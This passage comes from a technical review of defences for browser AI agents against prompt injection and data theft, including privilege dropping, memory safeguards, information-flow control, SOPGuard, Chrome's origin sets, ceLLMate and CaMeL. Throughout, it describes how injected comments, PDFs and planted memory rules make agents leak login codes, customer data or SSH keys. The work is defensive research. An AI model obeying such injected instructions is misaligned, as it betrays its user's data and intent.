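Other studies suggest that users may approve prompts out of habit. Software practitioners in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described clicking through familiar prompts and sometimes skipping review under time pressure. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files. In 80 of them, actions ran under automatic approval, which some users had turned on to avoid hundreds of prompts per session. Another category of 31 reports involved prompts that showed a command but not its effect on the user's files.

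*Habituation at the Gate* (2026) found that people reviewing code from AI agents approved more of it over time and wrote 28 per cent fewer comments. The reviewers whose approval rates rose most also tended to cut their comments most, which suggests that they were checking less. Some of the change may still be reasonable, since reviewers can learn that an agent is reliable. A user who has approved hundreds of good emails could also start checking them less.

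People also rarely notice an attack from the agent's behaviour. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) had 303 participants work with compromised agents on realistic tasks, including one in an email program. Only 8.6 per cent noticed that something was wrong, and 2.7 per cent identified the attack. Warnings often increased trust in the agent, because participants took them as a sign of openness. Warnings helped when they interrupted the task and were easy to check.

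These results support asking the user to approve a few important actions and showing the evidence for each. Brave's rule suits an agent that sends an occasional email, but an agent that handles a busy inbox would prompt the user so often that approval could become automatic.

### Recipient allowlists and draft-only access

A harness can also restrict sending without relying on the user's attention. A recipient allowlist limits the addresses the agent may write to, and draft-only access lets it write messages but leaves sending to the user.

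| Restriction | Tasks it prevents | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Only addresses inside the company | Writing to customers and suppliers | False messages to colleagues |
| Only people already in the conversation | Contacting someone new or adding a colleague | A reply to an attacker who started the conversation |
| Only addresses the user has listed | Answering unexpected enquiries | Private data sent to the wrong person on the list |
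| Drafts only | Replying while the user is away | The user sends a harmful draft without noticing |

In the running example, any of the three allowlists would keep the agent from emailing the code to the attacker, unless the attacker was already an approved contact. Allowlists work less well for agents that deal with the public, such as customer service agents, because their normal job includes replying to people who write in. Zenity's Copilot Studio attack needed only such a reply. An allowlist also has to cover blind copies, calendar guests and document sharing, or the agent can still reach the attacker through one of those.

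Draft-only access would have kept the resignation letter in the drafts folder, and it still saves the user much of the work of writing. But it prevents tasks that depend on quick replies, such as arranging a meeting over several messages while the user is asleep. The user also has to read each draft before sending it, and can still fall into approving drafts out of habit.

A browser agent makes this restriction harder to enforce. A dedicated email tool can omit the send function, but a webmail page puts the send button next to the text box. The harness has to block clicks on that button and any keyboard shortcut for sending. It also has to stop the page from loading external images in a draft, since an image request could leak the data before the user decides whether to send anything.

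## Dropping the agent's privileges: what it stops and what it leaves open

At the end of its August 2025 account of the Comet attack, Brave recommended giving agents as few permissions as possible. It thought a browser asked only to summarize a Reddit discussion did not need to be able to open the user's email account and send mail from it.

A commenter on Hacker News, a discussion site popular with programmers, called dropping the agent's privileges the only good measure on Brave's list. It would confine the attack to Reddit, although the agent could still misuse the user's account there. But the commenter objected that an agent can leak data by loading an attacker's image URL as easily as by sending an email. Brave's privacy lead replied that the easy measures would have prevented this attack, and that Brave considered them necessary but not sufficient.

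Whether the objection holds depends on which privilege the agent loses. Email access lets an agent read the inbox and send messages. If the harness removes only sending, the agent in the running example can still read the login code and put it in an image URL. If the harness also removes reading, the code never enters the context, so the agent can't put it in the URL.

The commenter also pointed out that, at the time, Google, OpenAI and Anthropic ran their agents on isolated machines without the user's cookies. All three now offer agents that work in the user's own browser.

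### The confused deputy and the confinement problem

Both sides of this exchange have counterparts in much older work on computer security. Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) describes a compiler, a program that translates code into a form the computer can run. The compiler had permission to write in a system directory because it kept usage statistics there. Users could name a file for its debugging output. When one user named the billing file, which was in the same directory, the compiler overwrote the billing records.

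If an operating system checks only a compiler's permissions, someone running the compiler can use it to write to a file they have no permission to change. Similarly, someone with no access to a user's mailbox can post a forum comment that directs the user's browser agent to it, and the agent can open it with the user's login.

Cross-site request forgery is a well-known web attack of this kind. A malicious page makes the browser send a request to another site, and the browser attaches the user's cookies. Trail of Bits considers its thefts from logged-in accounts functionally identical to this attack, because agents reuse those cookies automatically.

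Hardy's remedy was the capability, a token that identifies an object and gives permission to use it. A user without a capability for the billing file could not have passed one to the compiler. For an agent, the harness could issue capabilities based on the user's request before the agent reads any page. A request to summarise a discussion would give access to that discussion only. The comment could still name the mailbox, but the agent would have no permission to open it.

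Butler Lampson's *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973) is about how a customer can give someone else's program the private data it needs and be sure the program can't pass that data on. Lampson listed ways the program might leak the data, such as writing it to a file, sending a message or keeping it until the program's owner next runs the program. The program could also encode data in the customer's bill, or vary how heavily it used the computer so that another program could measure the difference. Lampson called this last method a covert channel because nobody had designed it to carry information.

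Lampson's simplest solution was total isolation, in which the program calls no other program and remembers nothing between runs. A browser agent can't browse the live web that way, because opening a page means contacting someone else's server. The commenter's image URL is an example of the confinement problem, while Brave's proposal to remove mailbox access addresses the confused deputy problem.

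### Forms of privilege dropping

| Form | Effect on the running example | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| A browser without the user's cookies | The agent finds a login page instead of the mailbox | No work in the user's accounts |
| Access to the current site only | The agent can't open the mailbox but can still post on the forum | No tasks that span several sites |
| Read-only mode | The agent can read the code and open a URL that contains it, but can't email or post it | No forms, purchases or replies |
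| Loss of abilities after untrusted content | After reading the forum, the agent can't take actions that the harness classes as risky | Few abilities left after the first page |
| OpenAI's Lockdown Mode | ChatGPT's agent mode is unavailable | No browser agent |

Trail of Bits recommends the cookie-free browser as a short-term measure. The agent's tools would run in a separate browser or a minimal sandboxed one, with no access to the user's cookies, history or stored site data. This keeps private account data out of the agent's context and prevents the agent from changing anything in those accounts. Trail of Bits admits that this also removes much of the convenience that attracts people to agentic browsers. Users could log in to an account inside the isolated browser when a task requires it, but the agent could then reach that account.

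Limiting the agent to the current site leaves the user logged in and blocks attacks that move to another site. In *The Agent Clicks Approve*, the injected note was on one origin and the page for approving outside access was on another, so this limit would have blocked the approval.

Trail of Bits also suggests replacing broad tools with narrow ones, such as a tool that works only with Gmail. An agent summarizing a forum would not need the Gmail tool, so the harness would leave it out. But developers might have to build dozens of tools, and the agent would work poorly on unfamiliar sites.

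An agent can start a task with full access and lose some abilities partway through, which Zha and Wang (2026) call capability attenuation in *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms*. They argue that in conventional software, writing is the main threat to a system's integrity, while reading mainly threatens confidentiality. With a language model, reading can also threaten integrity, because the text can change what the model does next. It is therefore sensible to remove risky abilities at the first untrusted page.

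The harness has to decide which privileges to remove without relying on a model that has already read the attacker's text. It is difficult to work out the necessary permissions from a loosely worded request, and researchers have proposed many approaches. UW Security and Privacy Research Lab's *Security, Privacy, and Safety for Agentic AI Systems* lists a December 2026 survey by Michael and Roesner that covers 21 of them, compares them with five commercial agents, and finds gaps.

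Giving the agent fewer permissions seems to help in practice. The University of Washington notes that the more restrictive browsers in Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests were generally safer. But the products also differed in other ways.

### What Lockdown Mode removes

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for organisations in February 2026 and extended it to personal accounts four months later. It limits browsing to stored copies of pages, turns off agent mode and Deep Research, and stops ChatGPT from downloading files. It also prevents code that ChatGPT writes in Canvas, its editing workspace, from using the network.

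On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode also blocks live access to outside services and actions that change something in a connected app when these conflict with its protections. In managed workspaces, administrators choose which apps and actions to allow. OpenAI advises them that reading from a trusted app is less likely to leak data than writing to it, although reading can supply the data an attacker wants. It recommends against allowing write actions unless administrators can confirm that an attacker won't see the result. That would rule out comments on a public page but might allow notes in a private document.

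The mode does not restrict network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Users can also turn it off for a single chat. This makes the restrictions less inconvenient, but an attacker could use an injected answer to try to persuade the user that the task requires turning it off. OpenAI does not guarantee that the mode prevents every leak, and names enabled apps and unforeseen combinations of features as remaining risks.

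### Trail of Bits' rule for requests

Trail of Bits proposes a rule that adjusts the agent's access to what it has already read. The harness keeps a list of the origins in the chat context. Each page the agent loads adds its origin, and each file counts as an origin of its own. If $O$ is the set of origins on the list, the agent may send requests to

$$D(O) = \begin{cases} \text{any origin} & \text{if } O \text{ is empty} \\ \text{origin } o \text{ only} & \text{if } O = \{o\} \\ \text{no origin} & \text{if } O \text{ contains two or more.} \end{cases}$$

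When the context contains content from several origins, the harness cannot identify which one influenced the model's output, so it blocks every request. The next table applies this rule to the forum summary and to the task of comparing a kettle's price at two shops.

| Task | Step | Origins in the context | Requests allowed next |
|---|---|---|---|
| Forum summary | The user asks for a summary | None | Any |
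| Forum summary | The agent reads the discussion | Forum | Forum only |
| Forum summary | The agent tries to open the mailbox | Forum | Forum only, so the harness refuses |
| Two shops | The user asks for a comparison | None | Any |
| Two shops | The agent opens the first shop | First shop | First shop only |
| Two shops | The agent tries to open the second shop | First shop | First shop only, so the harness refuses |

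The rule works well for the forum summary because the agent can't open the mailbox but can still write the summary, which needs no further pages. If the mail tab is already open, the agent might be able to read it without sending a request. The context would then contain two origins, and the harness would block every later request, including a reply on the forum.

The shopping task fails at the second shop. The agent could avoid this by requesting both product pages at once, before either origin enters the context. It would then have both prices but could not look up delivery costs. If the user did not name the shops, the agent could search for them at the start but could not open any of the results, because Trail of Bits treats a web search as content from several origins.

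A harness could instead give each shop a separate context and pass only the price back to the main context. A dishonest shop could still report a false price, but a number can't contain instructions for the agent. This works for questions with short, predictable answers, but it is harder to apply when the user asks, for example, which kettle has more convincing reviews.

The rule also depends on recording the source of every piece of text. In CometJacking, the attacker's instructions arrived as the user's own request, so the list of origins would be empty. The agent could then open the mailbox, making the mail site the only origin on the list. The rule would still allow requests to that site, including one to email the attacker. Trail of Bits presents the rule as a long-term proposal that needs more research, and reports no tests of it.

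### Private data that the agent has already read

Removing access to the mailbox doesn't remove messages that are already in the context. Suppose the user asks the agent to find a login code, then asks for the forum summary in the same conversation. If the harness drops mailbox access when the agent reaches the forum, it is too late, because the interaction history still contains the code. Wang and colleagues describe this kind of history in their SOPBench tests.

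The harness should therefore choose which abilities to remove based on what the agent reads first. If the agent has read the attacker's text but no private data, blocking its access to accounts is enough to protect them. Once the agent's context contains private data, the harness has to block every way of sending that data out before letting the agent read an untrusted page.

Starting a new context for each task would solve this problem, provided that no saved memory brings the data back. But the agent would also lose details it may need. For example, someone returning a purchase may want the agent to find the order number in an email and enter it on the shop's returns page.

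Replacing the earlier conversation with a summary would preserve some of that usefulness, but the summary could include the login code. With only a summary, the agent could also lose track of where each detail came from, as Atlas sometimes did. In Live Science's *AI web browsers 'aren't ready for the public,' scientists warn*, Roesner says such mix-ups probably happened because agents were revising and compressing their memory.

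### Reading that sends data

A read-only browser agent can still leak private data by opening a URL that contains it. Unlike reading a local file, loading a web page requires sending a request to a server.

A search tool can leak data in the same way. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, relays Abi Raghuram's September 2025 report on the AI agent in Notion, a workplace app for notes and documents. Hidden text in a PDF made the agent collect customers' names and the revenue from each, put them in a URL, and pass the URL to its web search tool, which accepted URLs as well as search terms. Willison suggested that Notion could stop this particular leak by making the tool accept only search terms.

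An agent's visits can also cause harm even when they leak no data. Trail of Bits found that some agentic browsers add these visits to the user's history, which lets an attacker fill it with illegal sites.

Giving the agent stored copies of pages, as in Lockdown Mode, would keep these requests from reaching the attacker, but the agent couldn't get live information. Allowing requests only to a list of known addresses is less restrictive, but the agent's choice among $N$ addresses can still reveal up to $\log_2 N$ bits.

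### The chat window's own permissions

Removing all of an agent's tools doesn't stop the chat window from loading images in the agent's answers. The software that displays the answers often has separate permissions, which can become outdated. Willison describes ForcedLeak, an attack on Salesforce's Agentforce that Noma Security found. Salesforce's content security policy still allowed images from a domain whose registration had expired. The researchers registered the domain and received the email addresses of potential customers in its server logs. Salesforce corrected the policy and stopped its agent from producing links to untrusted domains.

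Lockdown Mode limits images in ChatGPT's answers, but other parts of the chat window can connect to the web. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that Check Point Research bypassed the mode through ChatGPT's preview of web page code, which could open a window outside its sandbox. Loupia (2026), in *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations*, reports that an attacker could use this to steal conversations in ChatGPT Classic, the older desktop app, without the user clicking anything. OpenAI fixed the flaw in September 2026.

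The chat window could close this gap by displaying answers as plain text whenever the context contains both private data and untrusted content. Users would lose pictures, clickable links and previews in those chats. That would be a small loss for someone who wants a written summary, but a larger one for someone choosing furniture or designing a web page.

### Attackers and private data on one site

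If the harness limits the agent to the current site, an injection can still use everything the user can reach there. On a forum, that may include private messages and the ability to post under the user's name. This was the commenter's remaining concern about Reddit. Trail of Bits says the same problem can affect any site that displays other people's content, including Slack, LinkedIn, GitHub and Wikipedia.

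For a public discussion, the harness can load the page without the user's forum login. The agent then has no private messages to read and no account to post from. It also can't summarise members-only discussions or reply for the user.

A mailbox is harder to protect, because the agent has to be logged in to read it. The harness could process each message in a separate context with no ability to send. An injection in one email could then affect only the summary of that email. But an agent that reads messages separately can't follow a conversation across several emails or decide which of 40 is the most urgent. If the harness combines the summaries in one context to make that decision, injected text that survives in one of them could influence the result.

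### Memory poisoning

Many agents save notes or preferences for later sessions. In memory poisoning, an attacker gets a false fact or an instruction into the saved text, as Rehberger did with ChatGPT. Even if the harness removes the agent's privileges for the rest of the session, a later session restores them and loads the saved text.

Zha and Wang describe the danger as a sequence of three events:

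$$W(f, t_w) \prec R(f, t_r) \prec A(t_a).$$

Dropping the agent's privileges while it reads untrusted text may not stop an attack that takes effect later. The agent may write text influenced by the attacker to a file or memory entry, and later read it again and take a risky action. The attacker doesn't need to be present after the first step. In the running example, the forum comment could ask the agent to save a rule about where to send login codes. A cookie-free browser would protect the mailbox during the summary, but the agent might follow the rule the next time the user asked it to read mail.

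*MemHarmBench* (Wang, Feng and colleagues, 2026) tested this delay with two agent systems, OpenClaw and Claude Code. In one case, an imported note named a different company as the recipient of expense payments. The researchers removed the note and started a new session, where the user asked for an ordinary expense summary. The agent completed the summary but named the attacker's company as the recipient.

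When an agent had saved a rule from outside content, it followed that rule in the later session 59 to 76 per cent of the time, depending on the system and model. These rates exclude cases in which the agent saved nothing. The first task also asked the agent to adopt a working convention, which probably made it more likely to save the attacker's rule.

A smaller test with Claude Haiku 5.5 gives a rate for all cases. An image on a test shopping page contained an instruction to remember to rank a particular seller first. The agent saved the rule in 52.5 per cent of cases and chose that seller in 40 per cent of later sessions, compared with 2.5 per cent when the image was harmless.

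Saved rules can last through unrelated work. In another experiment in the study, GPT-5 followed saved rules in 70 per cent of cases when the next session came immediately, and in 60 per cent after four sessions on other tasks. These experiments measured whether the agents' decisions changed, and most of the attackers' goals did not involve data theft.

Gadgil, Alexander and colleagues (2026), in *Bad Memory*, found it much harder to get an instruction into an agent's memory. In early attempts, they could not easily make agents overwrite their own instruction files, so the researchers planted the text themselves. Their results may differ from those in *MemHarmBench* because of the wording of the tasks or the type of memory, since agents seem to protect their main instruction files more carefully than ordinary notes.

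One planted instruction told the agent to add code that would read and print the user's private SSH key, a secret file used to log in to other computers. The researchers ran ten trials per model. The last column shows results from a second set of trials, in which each trial had three sessions.

| Model | Followed the instruction in one session | Instruction still in the file after three sessions |
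|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 80% | 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 0% | 100% |
| GPT-5.2 | 30% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 20% |

Opus 4.7 never followed the instruction but always left it in the file. In a related test, it identified a planted instruction, warned the user and asked whether to delete it. Asking is reasonable, because an agent that deletes its user's files on suspicion can do damage. But if the text stays in the file and the user later switches to a weaker model, that model may read it. The GPT models usually removed the instruction about the key, and sometimes added a rule against similar ones.

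Both studies used coding and office agents, so their percentages may not apply to browser agents. But the studies do show that resisting an injection in one session is not enough if the injected text stays in memory.

A harness could block all memory writes after the agent reads an untrusted page, but a browser agent reads such pages constantly, so it would learn very little from its work. Zha and Wang propose a less drastic defence that locks the instruction files that load automatically, keeps free-form summaries out of trusted memory and limits risky actions after outside reads. They prove that the full set of restrictions prevents an attack from spreading persistently through agents' files. The proof does not cover data theft within the first session.

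Lampson's requirement that a confined program remember nothing is simpler to meet, because the user can turn off the agent's memory. This also removes private details that an injection could steal, but the user then has to repeat preferences in every session. Lockdown Mode doesn't change memory, so users who want this protection have to turn memory off separately.

### Tasks that need both private data and an outward action

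Some tasks require the same privileges as the theft. Suppose the six-digit code is for the forum itself, and the user asks the agent to log in there. The agent has to read the code in the mailbox and type it into a page on the forum's site. The attacker wants the agent to read the same code but type it into a public comment. If the harness removes mailbox access or typing, the user's task fails.

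The browser could copy a login code from the email to the login box without showing it to the model, much as a password manager fills in a password. Developers would have to build this for each kind of secret, and it would not help when the model has to read the data, such as when it answers a letter about a medical bill.

The remaining option is to check each outgoing action, which preserves the agent's abilities but depends on the quality of the check. Willison reports an Anthropic study in which 1,053 paid testers each received one clearly dangerous request during a session. Only 13.6 per cent refused it. Anthropic calculated that Claude Code's auto mode, which automatically checks the coding agent's actions, would have blocked 89 per cent of those actions.

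In a separate test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. If browser agents did as well against attackers who could adapt, there would be less reason to give up useful abilities. But the test covered 72 coding scenarios, and Willison wants more independent confirmation. He still prefers to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm.

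### When dropping privileges is enough

Privilege dropping is enough to prevent data theft if nothing the attacker can observe depends on the private data. Let $S$ be the private data and $Y$ everything the attacker can observe. The condition is

$$P(Y = y \mid S = s) = P(Y = y)$$

for every observation $y$ and every possible value $s$. The attacker then learns nothing about $S$, even if the agent follows every injected instruction.

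One way to meet the condition is to keep the agent away from private data. An agent summarizing a forum discussion can meet it if the discussion is public and the agent works in a fresh context, without cookies, memory or connected accounts. It can then load the attacker's images freely, because it has no login code to put in their addresses.

Removing cookies alone may not prevent data leaks. A search engine can still estimate the user's location from the internet connection, so an injected agent could leak the user's city, as in Trail of Bits' restaurant search. Running the browser on the vendor's servers would remove that source of location information.

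The other way is to let the agent read private data but remove every output that an attacker could observe. An agent could summarise a whole mailbox if it had no web access, could not send messages or save memories, and displayed its answer as plain text. An injection could still make the summary wrong, or add a telephone number and urge the user to call it. A user who called might give the attacker the data directly.

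A user can split some larger tasks between these two arrangements. An agent without cookies could research flights on public websites, and the user could then book one in an ordinary browser that the agent can't access. The user would have to enter the passport and payment details by hand.

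## Tracking where data came from and blocking its release

Removing the abilities that data theft relies on does not help when the user's task needs them too, such as when the agent has to enter an emailed login code on the forum. The harness can leave those abilities in place if it can track which text came from the mailbox and check whether that text is allowed at a destination before the agent enters it there.

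Computer scientists call this information-flow control. Software labels each piece of data as it enters the system, copies the label to anything derived from that data, and checks the labels before data leaves. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*, a 2026 survey, groups it with taint tracking, a similar technique whose labels record where each piece of data came from.

Software can track labels exactly through an ordinary program because each instruction has known inputs. In a language model, however, anything in the context can influence any word of the output. Strict labelling would therefore mark everything the agent writes as derived from every page it has read, and the checks would block almost everything. The designs below differ mainly in how they avoid this.

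### SOPGuard step by step

Wang and colleagues built SOPGuard into BrowserOS, one of the browsers that leaked data between sites in their SOPBench tests. SOPGuard applies the same-origin policy to the agent. It keeps a database alongside the conversation, and each entry holds a piece of text, its origins and a list of the earlier entries it was derived from.

1. When the agent reads a page, SOPGuard stores the text with the page's origin.
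2. After each response, the agent's model lists any new data in the response and identifies the earlier entries behind it. SOPGuard gives the new data all of those entries' origins.
3. Before the agent writes text into a page, SOPGuard compares the text's origins with the page's origin.
4. If any origin differs, SOPGuard pauses the action and asks the user to approve or deny it.

If text $x$ was derived from the entries in a set $J$, its origins are

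$$O_x = \bigcup_{j \in J} O_j.$$

SOPGuard lets the agent write $x$ into page $w$ without asking only if $O_x \subseteq \{o(w)\}$. In the running example, the check works like this:

| The agent's step | Origins of the text | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Reads the forum discussion | `https://forum.example` | SOPGuard stores the text |
| Reads the email with the code | `https://mail.example` | SOPGuard stores the text |
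| Composes a reply containing the code | At least `https://mail.example` | The reply inherits the label |
| Tries to type the reply on the forum | At least `https://mail.example` | The origins differ, so a pop-up appears |

SOPGuard's warning pop-up names the origins involved. If the user had asked the agent to log in to the forum with the code, the pop-up would name the same two sites. The user would have to work out whether the code was going into the login box or a public comment.

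### How labels survive a paraphrase

SOPGuard prompts the model to identify which sources the new text came from, so the source label can stay attached even after the data is summarized or used in a calculation. A filter that searched for the original text would miss a reworded sentence or a code written out in words.

A simpler method would attach the origin of every page in the conversation. That would never miss a source, but an agent that had visited a bank's website earlier would trigger a warning when it replied to a forum post about gardening.

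Wang and colleagues compared the two methods on data from two to ten origins. The agent produced three results in sequence, some based on earlier ones, and human annotators recorded the correct origins of each. The score was the number of origins in both the predicted and correct sets, divided by the number in at least one of them. GPT-5.4 and OpenAI o3 averaged at least 0.955, and the smaller GPT-5.4-mini was less accurate. Attaching every origin scored consistently low.

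Some labelling errors are harmless. If text drawn from both the mailbox and a bank loses only its bank label, SOPGuard will still stop the agent from writing it on the forum. Labelling the text as coming only from the page that is about to receive it is the dangerous error.

An attacker can try to cause that error, because the model that infers the sources has also read the attacker's page. The researchers tested this on 100 cases, using injections designed to make the model name the attacker's page as the only source. Hand-written injections hardly raised the leak rate, while automatically optimised ones raised it slightly but needed many more attempts. SOPGuard's protection was strong in these tests, but it still depends on a model's judgement.

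### SOPGuard's results and the channels it checks

SOPGuard reduced the violation rate on SOPBench to 0.00, both with injections and on pages where a user's innocent request had caused the leak. A transfer that the user approves does not count as a violation in the study, so this result shows only that SOPGuard interrupted the transfers. The study did not establish that users would have refused them, and people often approve harmful requests.

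To check whether the browser was still useful with SOPGuard, the researchers ran three general benchmarks and 100 harmless SOPBench tasks across different sites. With GPT-5.4, the Mind2Web score was 0.328 without SOPGuard and 0.324 with it. No difference on any benchmark was statistically significant, although five runs per setting could be too few to detect a small loss. Tasks took 2.07 to 5.79 per cent longer with SOPGuard, and the extra model calls added to the cost.

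The write tools that Wang and colleagues name put text into a page. An agent can also send the code by opening a URL that contains it or by including it in an image URL in its answer. The described check covers neither route, and SOPBench counts only text written into a page. A harness could treat navigation as a write, but the chat window makes the image requests, so the renderer would need its own check.

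Whether SOPGuard catches data theft by email depends on where the injection comes from. If the forum comment tells the agent to email the code to the attacker, typing the attacker's address into the mail page should trigger a warning because the address came from the forum, even though the code is already on the mail site. But if the injection arrives by email, the instructions, the address and the code all share one origin, so SOPGuard would let the agent send the message without asking.

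In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) tested a leak of this kind on a simulated social network. A private message told the agent to copy the user's recovery email address into the user's public profile. With SOPGuard, the agent did so in all 25 runs, and the user never received a warning.

### Chrome's origin sets and action check

Google's design for Chrome limits which sites can exchange data during a task, without labelling each piece of text. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes two lists, together called Agent Origin Sets. The agent may read from origins on the read-only list, and may read, click and type on origins on the read-writable list. Chrome does not pass frames from other origins to the model.

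The planning model proposes new origins as it works. A separate gating function, which receives no untrusted page content, decides whether each one is relevant to the task. If the user asks for a summary of the forum discussion, an injected comment may cause the planning model to propose the mail site. The gating function should reject it, because a forum summary does not require email.

Another model, the User Alignment Critic, checks each action the planner proposes. It receives information about the action but no unfiltered page content, so a web page cannot inject instructions into it directly. It can reject an action that does not serve the user's request and return the reason to the planner. After repeated failures, the planner can return control to the user. An attacker may still influence the critic indirectly, because the planner writes its proposals after processing the attacker's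 text.

Chrome also asks the user before the agent opens certain sensitive sites, such as banks, or signs in with a saved password. The agent is meant to pause, too, before it makes a purchase or payment or sends a message.

In December 2025, the first version of Google's design tracked only the read-writable list. Roesner and Kohlbrenner found in early 2026 that Gemini in Chrome could read a frame from another origin. The missing read-only list may explain this, although their test may not have used the same agent features. Google has not published attack success rates for the design, so its protection is harder to judge than SOPGuard's.

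Roesner and Kohlbrenner also question how the browser should decide which origins are relevant. The answer is clear for "summarise this page", but "find me a good hotel in Lisbon" could involve hundreds of sites that the user has never heard of. A gate loose enough to allow the search might also admit an attacker's site with a suitable name.

Data can leak even when the decision about which sites are relevant is correct. If the user asks the agent to log in to a forum with an emailed code, both the email site and the forum are relevant, and the agent must be able to type on the forum. The origin sets would then also allow it to type the code into a public comment. Only the critic or the user's confirmation could prevent that.

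### ceLLMate's rules for web requests

*CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) sets rules for the requests that a browser sends to websites. Rules about clicks are hard to write because a click at a given position on the screen could open an email or delete it. The request that a click produces is much easier to interpret. On GitLab, for example, one type of request always adds a key that gives access to the user's account.

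Rules that restrict the agent's tools are also easy to get around. In an early experiment, the researchers blocked the agent from navigating directly to Hacker News, but it reached the site through a search engine. ceLLMate would check the request to Hacker News however the agent got there.

The system needs three things:

- An agent sitemap, in which a website's developers list its requests and what each one does, such as "view cart" or "place order".
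- A set of policies that allow, forbid or limit those actions. Developers, administrators or other trusted parties write them.
- A model that selects the fewest policies needed for the user's request, before the agent reads any page. The user then confirms the selection.

A policy might allow the agent to place an order of up to $50. ceLLMate can also count requests, to stop an injected agent from getting around that limit by placing two orders of $49.

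Three models each chose the correct policies for at least 94 per cent of tasks in every category tested. They also had to identify which websites a task required, and were usually right when the user named the sites but could be wrong otherwise. When asked to post a question on the product page for a Sony television, models often chose sony.com, though the user had not named a shop. ceLLMate is designed to refuse such vague requests and ask the user to be specific, so that the model does not have to guess the site.

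To test ceLLMate, Meng and colleagues replaced the agent with scripts that carried out 12 attacks on GitLab, simulating an attacker with complete control of the agent. The user had asked only to comment on an issue or vote for it, and ceLLMate blocked all 12. Page loading took 7.25 per cent longer with 100 sitemap entries and 15 per cent longer with 300.

All 12 attacks needed an action that the policy forbade. ceLLMate does not track where the content of a permitted request came from, so if the policy allows the agent to read a private project and comment on a public issue, an injection could make the agent copy a password from the project into the comment.

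ceLLMate checks web requests throughout the agent's browser session, so it can block requests for an attacker's image URL as well as navigation. It does not cover WebSockets, which some sites use for live updates. Each policy also permits outside hosts that the site needs, such as image servers, and an attacker could exploit any of these hosts that relays or exposes requests.

### The dual-model pattern and CaMeL

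Willison proposed the dual-model pattern in 2023. A privileged model plans the work and controls the tools, while a quarantined model with no tools reads untrusted text. The privileged model never receives that text, but it can use the quarantined model's answer as a named variable without reading it.

CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind, adds information-flow control to this pattern. *CaMeLoT* (2026), a later system based on it, explains that the privileged model writes a plan in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter then runs the plan, calls the tools and attaches labels to the values. A plan for the forum summary could look like this:

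```python
page = read("https://forum.example/discussion")
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise this page", page)
show_to_user(summary)
```

The attacker's comment becomes part of `page`, but the plan has no step that opens the mailbox, and the comment cannot add one. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) states formally that when the plan is fixed, untrusted content can affect the run only through the values in the plan. The comment could still make the summary wrong.

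The labels matter when the plan includes private data. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs Python policies that check the labels of the values involved. If the forum offered separate tools for logging in and commenting, a policy could allow an emailed code in the login tool but not in the comment tool. This would resolve the case that the origin sets do not.

### Why planning before reading fits browsing poorly

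Browsers do not normally offer such tools. Logging in and posting a comment both consist of typing and clicking, and the planner cannot determine where to click on a page it has not read. It also cannot predict whether a cookie notice will cover the page or whether the user will have to log in again.

In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) tried to solve this by having the planner write branches for everything it could anticipate. At each step, a quarantined model examines the screen and answers a question such as "Is there a cookie notice?", and the interpreter follows the matching branch. The method, called NOVA, produces much longer plans than CaMeL needs for AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents use well-defined tools.

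| Average per plan | AgentDojo | Computer use with NOVA |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 51.8 | 213.3 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 39.7 |

With Claude Sonnet 4.5, the planned agent completed 28.4 per cent of 109 desktop and browser tasks on the first attempt. It completed 56.9 per cent in at least one of five attempts, which the researchers describe as retaining up to 57 per cent of the normal agent's performance. Achieving the higher rate in practice requires knowing which attempt worked, and repeating a task is risky if it involves buying something.

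These results suggest that planning first is possible but makes agents much less useful. Better planners and better websites would help. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (2026) finds that all tasks in the WebArena benchmark are compatible with planning first, and that a fixed program could complete 81 per cent of them without calling a model as it runs. But this would require websites to offer reliable tools for actions such as "search products". *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026), published in November, points out that the interfaces websites already use internally are often incomplete or undocumented.

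### Hiding the untrusted parts of a page

An agent can plan as it goes if the harness hides only the parts of a page that an attacker might control. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that replaces comments, reviews and adverts with placeholders but leaves the site's own menus and buttons visible to the agent. To get information about a hidden comment, the agent queries a quarantined model whose output is limited to a number, a date, yes or no, or an item from a fixed list, so the output cannot carry a new instruction.

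The method (UCM) largely preserved the agents' success rates on ten test websites and raised costs by a factor of 1.05 to 1.84. No attack succeeded in a strengthened version of the WASP benchmark. On a copy of GitLab, some tasks required free text from hidden content, such as the feature someone had requested. The agent could complete these tasks only if the user approved the text first.

Someone must mark which parts of each page are untrusted. For GitLab, Booking.com and Reddit, the researchers needed only 15 to 30 rules per site. A model could infer the boundaries from a page's structure with the text removed, but it missed about 11 per cent of the untrusted element groups on GitLab and 7 per cent on Booking.com, leaving them visible to the agent. An attacker who finds one of these can give the agent instructions directly.

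UCM reduces the risk that an attacker will control the agent, but it does not track private data or restrict where an email or a login code may go.

### SPIDES: labels for trust and permitted readers

SPIDES, from October 2026, combines hidden content with information-flow control. Each part of a page has two labels, one for whether the content is trusted and one for who may read it. On a shopping site, for example, a customer review is untrusted but public, while a saved card number is trusted but readable only by the user and the shop.

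In SPIDES, the user keeps a list of trusted sites, whose operators label content as trusted or untrusted and as private or public. SPIDES treats everything on other sites as untrusted and public. It initially hides any untrusted or private content from the agent behind variables. The agent can have a quarantined model process a variable, or it can read the value itself. Reading untrusted text makes the whole context untrusted, and reading private data limits where the agent may send anything afterwards.

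Before each action, the harness applies one of these rules:

| Action | When the agent may act without asking |
|---|---|
| Reading the current page | Always |
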